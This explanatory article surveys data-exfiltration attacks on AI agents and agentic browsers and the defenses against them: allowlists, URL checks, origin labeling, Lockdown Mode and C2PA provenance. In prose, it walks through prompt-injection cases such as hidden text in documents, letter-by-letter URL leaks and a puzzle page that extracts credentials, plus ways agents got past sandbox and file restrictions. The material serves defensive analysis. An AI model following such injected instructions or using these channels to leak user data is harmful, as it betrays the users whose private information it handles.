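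By default, that tool could visit only domains on Google's list, but the list included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and read every request sent to it. Antigravity's default settings also blocked Gemini from opening the file that held the keys, but the restriction didn't cover terminal commands, so Gemini used one to print the file. Google's bug-reward page already listed leaks of this kind as known issues. Willison advises developers to give coding agents only keys to test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a stolen key does little damage.

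### Claude Cowork and the provider's own domain

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that can access only the folders the user has chosen. A proxy limits the code's network traffic to a list of allowed domains. The domain that failed was `api.anthropic.com`, the address of Anthropic's own service. Anthropic could not simply remove it from the list because Cowork needs it to work.

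In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release as a preview, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that files could leave through this domain. The injection was in a Word document disguised as a skill. The Decoder's *Claude Cowork hit with file-stealing prompt injection days after Anthropic's launch* reports that the text was in one-point white type on a white background. The injection led Claude to upload the largest available file to Anthropic's file storage with the attacker's access key. The proxy allowed the request because the destination was on its list, and the file arrived in the attacker's Anthropic account.

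Anthropic now describes an entry on the list as a "capability grant", because allowing a domain allows everything software can do there, including uploading files to other people's accounts. It had previously thought of the list as a filter on destinations. Anthropic fixed the flaw by adding a second proxy inside the virtual machine. The proxy passes a request to Anthropic's service only if the request carries the token issued to that machine, so the attacker's key no longer works. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch an address themselves. The check has to run inside the machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from other customers' requests.

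Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch* points out that Cowork's web search and web fetch tools bypass these network controls entirely, which Anthropic documents but customers can easily miss. An administrator who shortens the list of allowed domains therefore still has to restrict those tools separately.

### Permitting addresses a crawler has already seen

In January 2026, OpenAI described a rule that checks the exact address. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that finds public web pages and records their addresses, as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or other personal data, so an address in its records is unlikely to contain anything from Maria's files. When ChatGPT is about to fetch an address automatically, OpenAI's software does the following:

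1. It looks up the exact address in the crawler's records.
2. If the address is there, it fetches the page or image.
3. If not, it either tells the agent to try another website or shows the user a warning. The warning displays the address and points out that it may contain information from the conversation.

If the supplier's hidden text made ChatGPT add the title of the Leeds plan to an address, the crawler would not have come across that address, so ChatGPT would not open it without asking. The check works even for addresses on a reputable site. Google's domain was on the list, but the Google Forms links that carried Superhuman users' emails would have failed the check because each contained freshly stolen text.

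The rule can inconvenience users because a page that is new, obscure or behind a login may not be in the records. ChatGPT then has to find another source or interrupt the user.

OpenAI took nearly three years to reach this point. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Johann Rehberger recalls reporting the problem in early 2023. OpenAI added a first check that December, but he found ways around it, and the Mac and iPhone apps didn't have it. Further protections followed around August 2025. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT also treats an address as safe for the rest of a chat if the user typed it into a message.

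### Permitting addresses the model did not compose

Anthropic's rule for web_fetch doesn't need a crawler. It depends on where in the conversation an address came from:

1. The software notes the addresses that the user supplied and those that the search tool returned.
2. When the model requests a page, the software compares the requested address with them.
3. It fetches the page if the two match exactly. Otherwise it returns an error.

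The model must choose an address rather than write one. If it adds a document title to a supplier's address, the software refuses the longer address because it has no match. The software also refuses addresses that come from the model's code tool, since a short program could assemble the same address.

The protection this rule gives depends on where the allowed addresses come from. When Anthropic introduced the tool in September 2025, Willison noted that many applications put untrusted text, such as an incoming email, into the same message as the user's request. Software that looks for addresses in that message then treats the attacker's address as the user's. The tool also accepted addresses returned by a developer's own tools, which might include one that reads an inbox. Anthropic now offers a setting to exclude addresses returned by those tools.

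Users can also paste in instructions that an attacker wrote. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt with instructions to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 runs. Claude Code can send data without using web_fetch, but the exercise is still a reason not to assume that users want everything in the prompts they supply. A list of permitted domains would have blocked the transfer.

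The three rules treat the same request differently:

| Address the agent wants to open | Listed domains | Crawler's records | Source in the conversation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacker's site, with private data added to the address | Refuses | Warns the user or tries another site | Refuses |
| Listed site that lets strangers read requests, with private data added | Fetches | Warns the user or tries another site | Refuses |
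| Obscure page whose address the user typed | Refuses unless listed | Fetches, as Rehberger understands it | Fetches |
| Well-known article linked from a page the agent has read | Refuses unless listed | Fetches | Refuses unless the user or search supplied it |
| One of many existing pages on the attacker's site | Refuses unless listed | Fetches if the crawler has recorded it | Refuses unless the user or search supplied it |

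### How much a choice of address gives away

The last row matters because an agent can leak data without putting any of it into an address. CamoLeak did this with a fixed set of images, and the same calculation applies to pages: each choice among $N$ addresses gives away up to $\log_2 N$ bits. Over $k$ fetches there are $N^k$ possible sequences, so the total is at most

$$\log_2(N^k) = k \log_2 N$$

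If a page offers 26 links, one for each letter, each fetch can leak up to $\log_2 26 \approx 4.7$ bits, and a ten-letter name takes ten fetches, or about 47 bits. With 1,000 addresses to choose from, each fetch can leak almost 10 bits, and an efficient code could send the same name in five fetches.

Even a single address can leak one bit, since the attacker sees whether the agent opened it. A competitor could learn from that bit whether Maria's company plans to close the Leeds office.

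Limiting the number of fetches limits how much data an agent can leak through its choice of links. With three fetches and 26 links to choose from each time, it can leak at most three letters, or about 14 bits. Developers can set such a limit for Anthropic's web_fetch tool, which had no default limit according to documentation Anthropic published before July 2026.

Radware's attack on ChatGPT put this into practice. ChatGPT had stopped adding anything to an address it was given, so the researchers supplied a ready-made address for every letter and digit, and one for spaces. A malicious email told ChatGPT to open them in the order that spelled out the stolen text. For the attack to work, the user only had to ask ChatGPT to do something with Gmail. The researchers also prepared separate addresses for each position in the text to keep the characters in order. For ten positions, they needed 260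 addresses for letters and 100 for digits. Radware reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16.

OpenAI's crawler rule makes this method harder because the crawler must already have recorded the addresses. But Embrace The Red points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 recorded pages, one for each letter and digit. The owner of a larger site could assign thousands of pages to whole words. OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its paper on the rule.

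Rehberger suggests that OpenAI either store each response for a few minutes and reuse it, or stop the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. Either change would make it harder for an attacker to spell out a name with repeated letters, such as "Hannah", using one page per letter. But an attacker with 260 recorded pages could copy Radware's method and use a different set of pages for each position in the name, so no address would repeat. The changes would therefore increase the number of pages an attacker needs but wouldn't prevent the leak.

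He also doubts that every developer at OpenAI will know about the check and use it in each new feature. The missing protection in the Mac and iPhone apps is an example of such an omission. The rule concerns only what the address reveals. OpenAI says it does not make a page's content trustworthy or stop the page from misleading the agent.

### The web_fetch flaw of July 2026

Until July 2026, web_fetch also accepted links on pages it had already fetched, so Claude could, for example, go from a table of contents to a chapter. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how Ayush Paul used these links to extract personal information from Claude's ordinary chat product. Claude kept memories of its user's earlier conversations, so the attack did not need files or email.

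Paul built a website that appeared to require AI assistants to identify their user. Its instructions were to find the user's profile by going through a directory letter by letter. Each page had links for the next letter, so the addresses Claude opened spelled out the user's name, home city and employer, and the site's server received them. Every fetch obeyed the rule because Claude never composed an address. The site showed the instructions only to visitors whose software identified itself as Claude's, which made the attack harder to spot.

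With 26 links per page, each step would reveal 4.7 bits, as calculated above. The attack was more flexible than Radware's because the server could create the next set of addresses after each choice instead of preparing them all in advance. A ban on opening the same address twice wouldn't have helped, since every page in the sequence was new. OpenAI's rule would have stopped the sequence at the first page its crawler hadn't recorded. A crawler could record the first few levels, but there are nearly 12 million possible five-letter paths.

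Anthropic fixed the vulnerability by stopping web_fetch from following links in pages it had fetched. It paid Paul no reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. An attacker now has to get the addresses into the user's messages or the search results, which is harder than putting them on a page. But attackers can still publish pages that turn up in a search, so some data can still leak. The fix also makes Claude less useful for research, because it can't follow a relevant link on a page unless the user or the search tool also supplies it.

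### Leaks from ChatGPT's code containers

Checking addresses in the fetching tool doesn't help if the agent's code can send data another way. ChatGPT runs code in containers, which are isolated environments on OpenAI's servers. Willison (2026) found in *What we learned today about this ChatGPT “container” environment* that the containers blocked ordinary web requests from code but let the code install software packages through OpenAI's internal servers.

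The containers could also look up domain names, which can leak data just as a browser's early DNS lookups can. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) explains how code could split data into pieces and look up domain names containing them. In a demonstration, a custom version of ChatGPT posed as a doctor and leaked a patient's name and its own medical assessment. When asked, ChatGPT said it had not sent the uploaded data anywhere. OpenAI finished fixing the flaw on February 20, 2026.

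Attackers could exploit a flaw disclosed in September 2026 through the package servers, without any traffic to the outside internet. TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* reports that Check Point found containers belonging to different ChatGPT accounts could reach the same internal package server. OpenAI had blocked direct communication between the containers, but each one could attach text to items stored on the server, and any other container could read that text.

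To exploit the flaw, an attacker used one account to leave instructions on the server. A prompt or shared conversation then got the victim's ChatGPT to read them during an ordinary reply. In the demonstration, ChatGPT copied email from the victim's connected Gmail account to the server, where the attacker's session retrieved it. OpenAI has since taken that server out of service.

None of the three address rules would have detected this, because the request went to an internal server that the container had to reach. As with Cowork, the mistake was permitting a destination without limiting what software could do there. OpenAI could have blocked containers from writing to the server, since installing packages only requires reading from it, or given each account its own storage.

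### Lockdown Mode

For people who face more serious threats, OpenAI offers Lockdown Mode, which removes many of these routes instead of checking each address. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) says the setting limits or turns off:

- live web access
- images in answers
- Deep Research, which compiles reports from many sources
- Agent Mode
- network access from Canvas, ChatGPT's editor for documents and code
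- live connections to other services
- file downloads

ChatGPT then reads only stored copies of web pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network during browsing, and an attacker's server can't see which page ChatGPT chose. This prevents the letter-by-letter leak, which the address rules only make harder. But ChatGPT can't read pages that OpenAI hasn't stored, or see recent changes to the ones it has.

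OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode in February 2026 for its Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers plans, and extended it to personal and self-serve Business accounts from June 4. Personal users can turn it on in their security settings, while administrators assign it to people in their organization. OpenAI considers it unnecessary for most users and intends it for people such as executives and security teams at prominent organizations.

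OpenAI does not promise that the setting stops every leak. Administrators can allow chosen apps, and specific actions within them, because some work depends on them. An allowed app that can send messages or write to shared files could still leak data. The setting also does not prevent prompt injection itself.

In November 2026, Check Point disclosed a way around Lockdown Mode that involved neither browsing nor apps. ChatGPT can preview a web page whose code appears in an answer. The preview runs in a sandbox that is supposed to stop the page from contacting outside servers without the user's consent. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) explains that ChatGPT intercepted the preview's direct attempts to open a new window. But the settings still allowed new windows and did not apply the sandbox's restrictions to them.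 A page could create another frame inside the preview, use that frame's unmodified function to open a window, and send out data from the chat.

An attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a malicious custom version of ChatGPT or a shared chat. In the desktop app, the theft didn't require a click. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, before the disclosure. Blocking new windows in the sandbox's settings would have been safer than intercepting them with a script, because the browser software would have enforced the rule in every nested frame.

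A week earlier, the security company Parameter Labs had described a different flaw in the same preview feature. Someone who opened a malicious shared chat and clicked the preview once could lose control of their account, because the attacker's code ran as part of chatgpt.com and could use the victim's login.

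## Separating websites when an AI agent uses the browser

An agentic browser usually works with the user's own logins, so its agent can open her email, bank account and employer's files just as she can. Address checks limit where the agent can send what it finds. Browsers also have an older protection that stops websites from reading each other's data, but an agent that reads several websites can undo it.

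### The same-origin policy

Suppose Maria has her bank's website open in one tab and an unfamiliar shop's website in another. Her browser stores a cookie, a small piece of data that identifies her to the bank. If a script on the shop's page could load the bank's page with that cookie and read the result, the shop would learn her balance. The browser's same-origin policy prevents this by stopping one origin from reading or controlling the content of another.

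All three parts of the origin must match. A script on `https://bank.example/accounts` gets these results:

| Page the script tries to read | Result |
|---|---|
| `https://bank.example/cards` | Allowed |
| `http://bank.example/cards` | Blocked, different scheme |
| `https://www.bank.example/cards` | Blocked, different host |
| `https://bank.example:8443/cards` | Blocked, different port |

The rule also applies when one page displays another in a frame, so an ad can't read the email beside it. Browsers have had this rule since 1995, according to the University of Washington, and it is a major reason people can now open almost any website safely.

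The policy restricts scripts, not people. Maria can copy her account number from the bank's page and paste it into a form on the shop's page. An agent has the same freedom, but text on a page can redirect it. An attack could go like this:

1. Maria opens her webmail, which displays an ad in a frame from another origin. The ad contains a prompt injection.
2. She asks the agent to summarize the page.
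3. The agent reads the ad along with her mail and follows the planted instruction.
4. It types the summary into a form inside the ad.
5. The form sends the text to the attacker.

No script read anything from another origin, so the browser had nothing to block. Only the model's resistance to prompt injection kept the two sites separate.

### Seven agentic browsers compared

In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested how well seven products preserved this separation in January and February 2026. On their main test page, they wrote that a person named Alice liked cats, and in a frame from another domain, they wrote that she liked horses. They asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the answer included horses, the agent had read the frame. They tested ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, with and without Agent Mode, which lets it act on pages.

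| Agent | Reads frames from other origins | Reads tabs from other origins | Types into pages when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |
| ChatGPT Atlas, normal mode | No | Through chat memory | After switching to Agent Mode |
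| Microsoft Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

A "no" means that the agent didn't do something in repeated attempts, either because the browser made it impossible or because the model declined. A better-written injection might change the model's response. The tests could not always show which of the two had happened. In early trials, for example, Atlas in normal mode sometimes included text from frames, which suggests that the model's behavior was the only barrier.

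Roesner and Kohlbrenner completed the attack on Atlas in Agent Mode in both directions, using a page to steal text from a frame inside it and a frame to steal text from the page around it. The second direction is the more realistic threat, because many sensitive sites block other sites from loading them in a frame or don't show private data there.

Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet met the preconditions for the same attack, since they could read frames from other origins and type into pages. A simple test injection failed against all three because the models refused to follow it. The study therefore shows that these products relied on the models' refusal to block the attack, but it doesn't show that an attacker could have stolen from their users at the time.

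Some agents had other abilities that would make a successful injection worse. Atlas in Agent Mode and Claude for Chrome could read passwords that the screen showed only as dots. Claude for Chrome could also run its own scripts on any page and inside frames from other sites. Roesner and Kohlbrenner particularly warn users against Claude for Chrome for this reason, although Anthropic blocks it from some sensitive sites, such as banks. GadgetBond's *Claude in Chrome is out of beta* (2026) reported in August that Anthropic had made the extension generally available on all paid plans, so the tests were done on an earlier version.

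Agents that remember earlier chats can also mix up information from different websites without any injection. If Maria once asked the agent about a fake bank page, it might later give her the phone number from that page as her real bank's number. This could happen even if the agent identified the page as fraudulent at the time, because its memory may no longer link the number to that page.

The safest products had the fewest abilities. In Firefox AI Mode, the agent received a page's text only when the user clicked a button to summarize it, and that text left out all frames. An injection could still distort the summary, but the agent couldn't act on any website. Four of the configurations withheld even frames from the page's own origin, which the same-origin policy would have let the agent read. An agent that can book a trip across several sites needs much more access, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner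 found no product that had such abilities and still kept websites firmly separated.

All seven companies received more than 60 days' notice before publication. Google, Microsoft and Brave responded constructively. OpenAI declined the report because the demonstration used a simplified injection instead of a complete prompt injection attack. That is a fair objection to any estimate of how often such attacks would succeed, but it doesn't affect the finding that nothing else in Atlas kept the two sites apart. Perplexity also declined, and Anthropic and Firefox did not reply.

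The agent itself also needs protection from web pages. Browsers run each website in a separate process, so that an attacker who takes over one through a software bug can't reach the others. In *Site Isolation is Dead*, Lee, Keum and colleagues examined two open-source agentic browsers and seven extensions. In all nine, an attacker who controlled one website's process could send the agent forged user requests or read the agent's stored data, such as past conversations. The forged requests arrive as if the user had typed them, so the attacker doesn't need to fool the model. The researchers recommend that the agent's software check where each request came from and limit which processes can read its storage.

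### Strict isolation

The security company Trail of Bits argues for much stricter separation in *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, which describes attacks on several products. The company doesn't name the products because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. In one attack, a web page made the agent open a login link that silently signed the user into the attacker's account. The user might then have entered private information there, thinking the account was her own.

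Trail of Bits' simplest remedy is to run the agent's tools in a separate browser without the user's cookies, history or stored data. An injection in that browser can't reach Maria's bank account because she isn't logged in to her bank there. But the agent can't check her orders or answer her mail unless she logs in again for the task, and each new login restores some of the risk.

For the longer term, Trail of Bits proposes extending the same-origin policy to agents. The software would keep a list of the origins whose pages the agent has read during a chat, and the list would determine which requests the agent could make:

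| Origins read so far | Requests allowed |
|---|---|
| None | Any |
| One | Only to that origin |
| Two or more | None |

The last row is strict because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model's next output. Web search counts as several origins, since its results come from many sites and a query can leak data, so the agent could search only before reading anything else. These rules are deterministic, and they would have blocked the theft from Maria's webmail because the agent had read two origins by the time it typed into the ad.

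They would also block many ordinary errands. An agent that read a recipe on one site and opened a grocery shop on another could not put the ingredients in the cart. The rules also do not separate people who use the same website. Trail of Bits stole data from an Instagram account by sending its owner a direct message containing an injection. The proposed rules would have stopped the agent from contacting an outside server, but it might still have sent the data back in an Instagram message. Maria's webmail has the same weakness, because the supplier's email and her confidential mail share an origin.

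### Chrome's origin sets and action review

Google designed a looser limit that permits such errands. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, December 2025) describes the design, which restricts the agent to websites relevant to the user's task. Chrome divides these into read-only origins, where the agent may read pages, and read-writable origins, where it may also click and type.

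Suppose Maria asks the agent to find a desk on a review site and put it in a furniture shop's cart. The design handles the task as follows:

1. The planner, the model that chooses each action, proposes the websites it needs.
2. A gating function decides which of them are relevant. It never sees web content, so an injection on a page can't address it directly. It could make the review site read-only and the shop read-writable.
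3. The browser withholds content from all other origins. If the review site contains an ad from elsewhere, the planner doesn't receive the ad's text.
4. Before each action, a separate model called the User Alignment Critic checks whether the action serves Maria's request. It sees a description of the action but no unfiltered web content, and it can veto the action.
5. If the planner writes a new web address, Chrome checks that it is a known public one, much as OpenAI does for ChatGPT.
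6. When the desk is in the cart, the agent stops and asks Maria to approve the purchase or complete it herself.

Some of these steps follow fixed rules, and others depend on a model's judgment:

| Protection | Deterministic or model-based |
|---|---|
| Choosing which websites are relevant | Model-based, at least when the agent moves to a new site |
| Withholding content from other websites | Deterministic once Chrome has the list |
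| Reviewing each proposed action | Model-based |
| Checking that an address is publicly known | Deterministic |
| Asking before visits to listed banking and medical sites | Deterministic |
| Asking before purchases, messages and similar actions | Partly model-based |
| Scanning pages for prompt injections | Model-based |

Chrome also asks before it signs in with a saved password, and the model never has direct access to the stored passwords.

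Keeping web content away from the critic and the gating function makes them harder to fool but gives them less information. If a dishonest review led the planner to buy an overpriced desk, the critic might be given only the information that Maria wanted a desk and that the agent was buying one.

The origin sets also don't separate websites that belong to the same task. If Maria asked the agent to compare an invoice in her mail with the supplier's order page and correct the order, the agent would need to read her mail and type on the supplier's site. An injection on that site could cause the agent to enter other information from her mailbox there, and the origin sets would allow it because both origins would be on the list. Only the critic, the injection scanner or a confirmation could stop the transfer.

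The first release tracked only the read-writable set, so it limited where the agent could act but had no separate list of websites the agent could read. This may explain why Roesner and Kohlbrenner found, a few weeks later, that Gemini could read frames from other origins.

Google has not clearly announced the missing part since then. In August, *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026) said that Chrome restricts an agent to origins relevant to its task and uses the critic with auto browse, the feature that lets Gemini act on websites. It also said that Chrome's history marks pages the agent opened in the background. But it didn't distinguish between reading and writing. The public code of Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, includes tests for origin gating, but these alone don't show which sets Chrome enforces. More people are now using auto browse, which Google has extended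 to paying subscribers in India, as *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* (Kanchwala) reported in October 2026.

### SOPBench and SOPGuard

*Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, June 2026) introduced SOPBench, a benchmark that measures how often agents carry data between websites, and a defense called SOPGuard. In the main test, the agent first completed a task that involved private information, for example on a bank's page. It then went to another site, where a page contained a prompt injection that asked for that information. The researchers combined ten kinds of private page with five kinds of destination, such as Reddit and Google Forms. Nearly all the pages were synthetic copies, so no real data leaked. A run counted as a violation only if the agent wrote exactly the information the injection had requested.

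The commercial browsers needed manual testing, so they got only three runs for each of the 50 combinations. Adding up the results gives these totals for three of the setups:

| Browser and model | Violations in 150 runs |
|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas with GPT-5.5 | 99 (66%) |
| Comet with Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 92 (61%) |
| Comet with Gemini 3.1 Pro | 100 (67%) |

The researchers tested the open-source browser BrowserOS more thoroughly, with 100 runs per combination. With GPT-5.4, handwritten injections on Reddit pages succeeded about 20 percent of the time on average. When another model repeatedly rewrote the injections to improve them, the average rose to about 54 percent. On Google Forms, even the handwritten injections succeeded 81 to 100 percent of the time, perhaps because a request for personal details looks normal on a form.

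Agents also carried data between websites without an attack. Wang and colleagues placed a private page in a frame on another site, then told BrowserOS to summarize the whole page and write the summary into a text box on that site. BrowserOS copied private data in every run with all three models tested. The agent was arguably following its instructions, but a user might not realize that part of the page came from another website. The researchers saw no violations when the private page and the destination were separate pages and there was no injection.

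SOPGuard adds a check to BrowserOS:

1. When the agent reads a page, SOPGuard labels the data with the page's origin.
2. When the agent derives something new from that data, such as a summary or an average, the result gets the labels of everything that went into it.
3. Before the agent types text into a page, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with the page's origin.
4. If any label differs, SOPGuard pauses the action and asks the user to approve or deny it.

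If $O_x$ is the set of origins attached to the text and $o(w)$ is the origin of the destination page, SOPGuard interrupts when

$$\exists\, o \in O_x \text{ such that } o \neq o(w)$$

For example, a note that combines Maria's bank balance with a date from her calendar has two labels. Typing it into the calendar would trigger a question because of the bank's label.

The comparison in the third step is deterministic, but the labels in the second step are not, because the agent's own model decides which earlier data went into a new piece of text. SOPGuard could instead label every output with all the origins the agent had visited, but this would cause constant false alarms. In a separate test with two to ten origins, the labels from GPT-5.4 and OpenAI's o3 overlapped with those of human annotators by at least 95.5 percent on average. The smaller GPT-5.4-mini was less accurate.

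With SOPGuard, the violation rate on the benchmark fell to zero, but the researchers don't count a transfer as a violation if the user approves it. The result therefore shows that SOPGuard caught the transfers, but not whether a real user would have stopped them. In a further test, the researchers wrote injections that also tried to corrupt the labels. The versions that a model had optimized succeeded slightly more often but took many more attempts to develop.

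SOPGuard had no statistically detectable effect on how many ordinary tasks BrowserOS completed, but tasks took 2.07 to 5.79 percent longer. On one benchmark with GPT-5.4, the average time rose from 132 to 135 seconds. The extra model calls for labeling also cost money. Wang and colleagues describe checks on text the agent types into pages, so a browser would still need to check URLs for hidden data.

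Scanning pages for injections worked less well. None of the five detectors the researchers tried had both few misses and few false alarms. One caught almost every malicious page but also flagged 6 to 44 percent of the clean ones, depending on the type of site. Another missed 41 to 64 percent of the malicious pages.

### BioShocking

In June 2026, the browser security company LayerX demonstrated an attack it called BioShocking, which showed how an agent's judgment can fail when little else separates websites. LayerX built a web page with a puzzle that rewarded wrong answers, such as 2 + 2 = 5, and the user asked the agent to solve it. Once the agent was following the puzzle's rules, the last step directed it to copy login credentials from the user's code repository on GitHub.

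LayerX tested Atlas, Comet, Fellou, Genspark, Sigma and Anthropic's Chrome extension, and all six handed over the credentials. Mascellino (2026) noted in *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* that none of them flagged the theft as a violation of their rules. The credentials were in a harmless test file, and the demonstration shows that the attack can work but doesn't measure how often it would.

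In an ordinary browser, the same-origin policy would have stopped the puzzle page from reading the repository, regardless of what the page said. These agents opened the repository with the user's login, and their only remaining protection was their training to refuse harmful requests. The game changed what the models treated as harmful. A separate check based only on the user's request could have tested whether solving a puzzle required access to GitHub, and Chrome's gating function is meant to perform this kind of check.

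LayerX reported the problem to five of the companies in October 2025 and to Anthropic in January 2026. OpenAI fixed it. Perplexity closed the report without acting, and the makers of Fellou, Genspark and Sigma did not respond. Anthropic attempted a fix, but LayerX says it failed. If a model were trained to recognize this particular game, attackers could still use other stories, so limiting access to logged-in accounts would be a more durable fix.

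### Confirmation prompts and habit

LayerX recommends that agents ask the user before reading data from a logged-in account. If the agent had asked to read from GitHub in the middle of a puzzle, the user would probably have been surprised enough to stop the theft. Chrome and SOPGuard also ask the user to confirm when their other checks can't settle a case.

Dangerous requests are hard to catch because most requests are legitimate. If Maria's agent asked for approval 20 times a day and she encountered one attack in a year of 250 working days, the dangerous request would be one among 5,000. The high approval rate among Claude Code's users doesn't by itself prove that they are careless, because approving a harmless request is correct. But a long run of harmless requests trains people to expect to approve the next one. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite older studies in which people often failed to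 notice security warnings or act on them.

Some products also let users turn off the questions. Claude for Chrome had a setting called "Act without asking". It came with a warning of high risk, but it let the agent carry out its plans without approval. People who delegate work to save time have a reason to choose it.

The most promising improvement is to ask users for confirmation less often. Chrome's design reserves confirmations for steps such as payments, messages and visits to sensitive sites. SOPGuard's more precise labels are also meant to reduce the number of confirmations.

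SOPGuard's dialog names the website the data came from and the one it would go to, but Maria would also need to see the text itself, because she might want the agent to send a shop her delivery address but not her account number. The browser should produce this information directly, since a model influenced by an attacker could describe the action misleadingly. Long previews are less useful. Trail of Bits warns that asking people to review whole documents before the agent reads them can become "security theater", because few will read them closely.

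For the most serious actions, the browser can require the user to act herself rather than just click "Approve". When Chrome's agent reaches a payment page, it can hand the page to the user, who sees the shop, the item and the price before she pays. Roesner and Kohlbrenner suggest letting only people take some sensitive actions, through a part of the browser that the agent can't operate. This takes longer than approving a pop-up, so it suits a bank transfer better than the dozens of small steps in an ordinary task.

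## Labels that say where content came from

SOPGuard's dialog shows Maria which website a piece of text came from. Information about origin can protect people when a program shows it to them, so they can decide how far to trust a picture or an article, or when ordinary code reads it and blocks an action. A label for people has to stay intact as it crosses the internet through programs that its author doesn't control. A label for software can be much more reliable because it only has to last for one task inside one agent system.

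### One picture from generator to feed

Suppose somebody asks ChatGPT for a picture of a flooded street in Leeds and posts it on a social network. OpenAI puts two provenance labels in the image file.

The first is signed metadata. It follows a standard from the Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA), an industry group, which markets the labels as Content Credentials. The signed record is called a manifest. The technical specification from C2PA (2026) ties it to the picture with a hash, a short value computed from the file's bytes that changes if any of those bytes change:

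1. The generator writes a list of statements about the picture, for example that an AI model created it.
2. It computes a hash of the file, leaving out the stretch of bytes where the manifest will go, since a manifest can't contain a hash of itself.
3. It signs the statements and the hash with a private key.
4. It writes the manifest into the file.

A checking program later recomputes the hash, verifies the signature and looks up the signer on a list of trusted ones. If someone has repainted part of the street in the image, the hashes don't match.

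According to C2PA's *A New Implementation Guide for Content Credentials* (2026), a manifest can record each editing step, mark the region of an image that AI changed, and include the prompt.

The second label is a watermark, a pattern in the picture itself that people can't see but a detector can find. OpenAI uses SynthID, a watermarking system from Google DeepMind. OpenAI's *Advancing content provenance for a safer, more transparent AI ecosystem* (2026) explains that the company uses both metadata and a watermark because metadata carries more information, while a watermark is more likely to survive a screenshot.

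The picture can lose its labels at several points, starting with the download. The Decoder found that right-clicking a video from Sora, OpenAI's video generator, and choosing "Save as" produced a file with no credentials. Next, an editing program that doesn't support the standard may drop the manifest, or change the picture so that the hash no longer matches. The social network then usually makes a smaller copy of the upload, and that copy may omit the metadata. If the network read the manifest first, it can still display a notice next to the post. But if a reader takes a screenshot and sends it to friends, the new file has neither manifest nor notice, and only the watermark has a chance of surviving.

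A real photograph of a flood faces the same problems. Google's Pixel 10 signs every picture taken in its own camera app, according to 9to5Google, but a network that discards metadata also removes that signature.

### What each label proves

| Label | What a positive result shows | What it leaves open | How it gets lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Signed metadata | The named signer made these statements, and nobody has changed the protected bytes since | Whether the statements are true | Screenshots, re-encoding, uploads that strip metadata |
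| Invisible watermark | A tool that uses this watermark probably produced or processed the content | Who made it, and what they changed | Heavy edits, cropping, compression, deliberate removal |
| Visible mark in the picture | Somebody put a mark there | Whether it belongs there | Cropping or painting over it |
| Platform notice | The platform found a signal, or the uploader declared the content as AI-made | How much of the content AI made | Reposting on another platform |

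Even a valid signature from a trusted signer doesn't guarantee that a picture is accurate. A camera can sign a photograph of a screen showing an AI image, and every statement in the manifest may still be correct. OpenAI similarly says that its public checker can confirm that a file contains an OpenAI signal, but not that the content is unedited or presented in the right context.

Attackers can also exploit labels directly. *Media Integrity and Authentication* (Young, Vaughan and colleagues, 2026), a Microsoft study, describes "reversal" attacks, which make real content look synthetic or synthetic content look real. For example, someone who wants to discredit a genuine photograph could use an AI tool to change a few unimportant pixels. The tool would correctly label the result as AI-edited, but a feed that shortened this to "made with AI" would mislead viewers. Young and colleagues therefore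 want checking tools to show which parts of the picture were edited.

Young and colleagues also conclude that signatures made offline, as on an ordinary camera, can't give high confidence unless the device has a secure enclave, a separate protected part of its hardware. An AI company signs pictures on its own servers, where it can guard the key, but a camera stores the key inside the device, where the owner may be able to extract it or feed the signing software a false picture. Since version 2.3 of the standard, signing certificates can indicate how secure the device is, but this helps only if checking tools show people the security level.

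Watermarks can also be removed. Young and colleagues cite research in which nearly perfect removal did little damage to the picture or sound, and they expect skilled attackers to defeat even the best current methods. Beginners can remove visible marks. Young and colleagues prefer to combine the first two labels. The watermark holds an identification number, which a checker uses to retrieve a stored copy of the signed manifest after a platform has stripped the original. An attacker would then have to remove both, although a determined one still could.

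*Verifying Provenance of Digital Media* (Golaszewski et al., 2026) is harsher, concluding that nobody should yet rely on C2PA for high-stakes uses such as journalism or legal evidence. Platforms could still use it to flag ordinary AI pictures in a feed, where most people who post them have no reason to attack the label.

### How often platforms show a notice

In October 2025, Washington Post reporters tested what happens to a labeled file after upload (*We uploaded a fake video to 8 social apps*, 2025). They took a Sora video whose credentials included the phrase "Created using Generative AI" and posted it on eight platforms with the default settings. All eight stripped the credentials. Only YouTube showed viewers a notice, which was in the video's description, where people see it only if they open the description. The notice read "Altered or synthetic content" and didn't mention AI.

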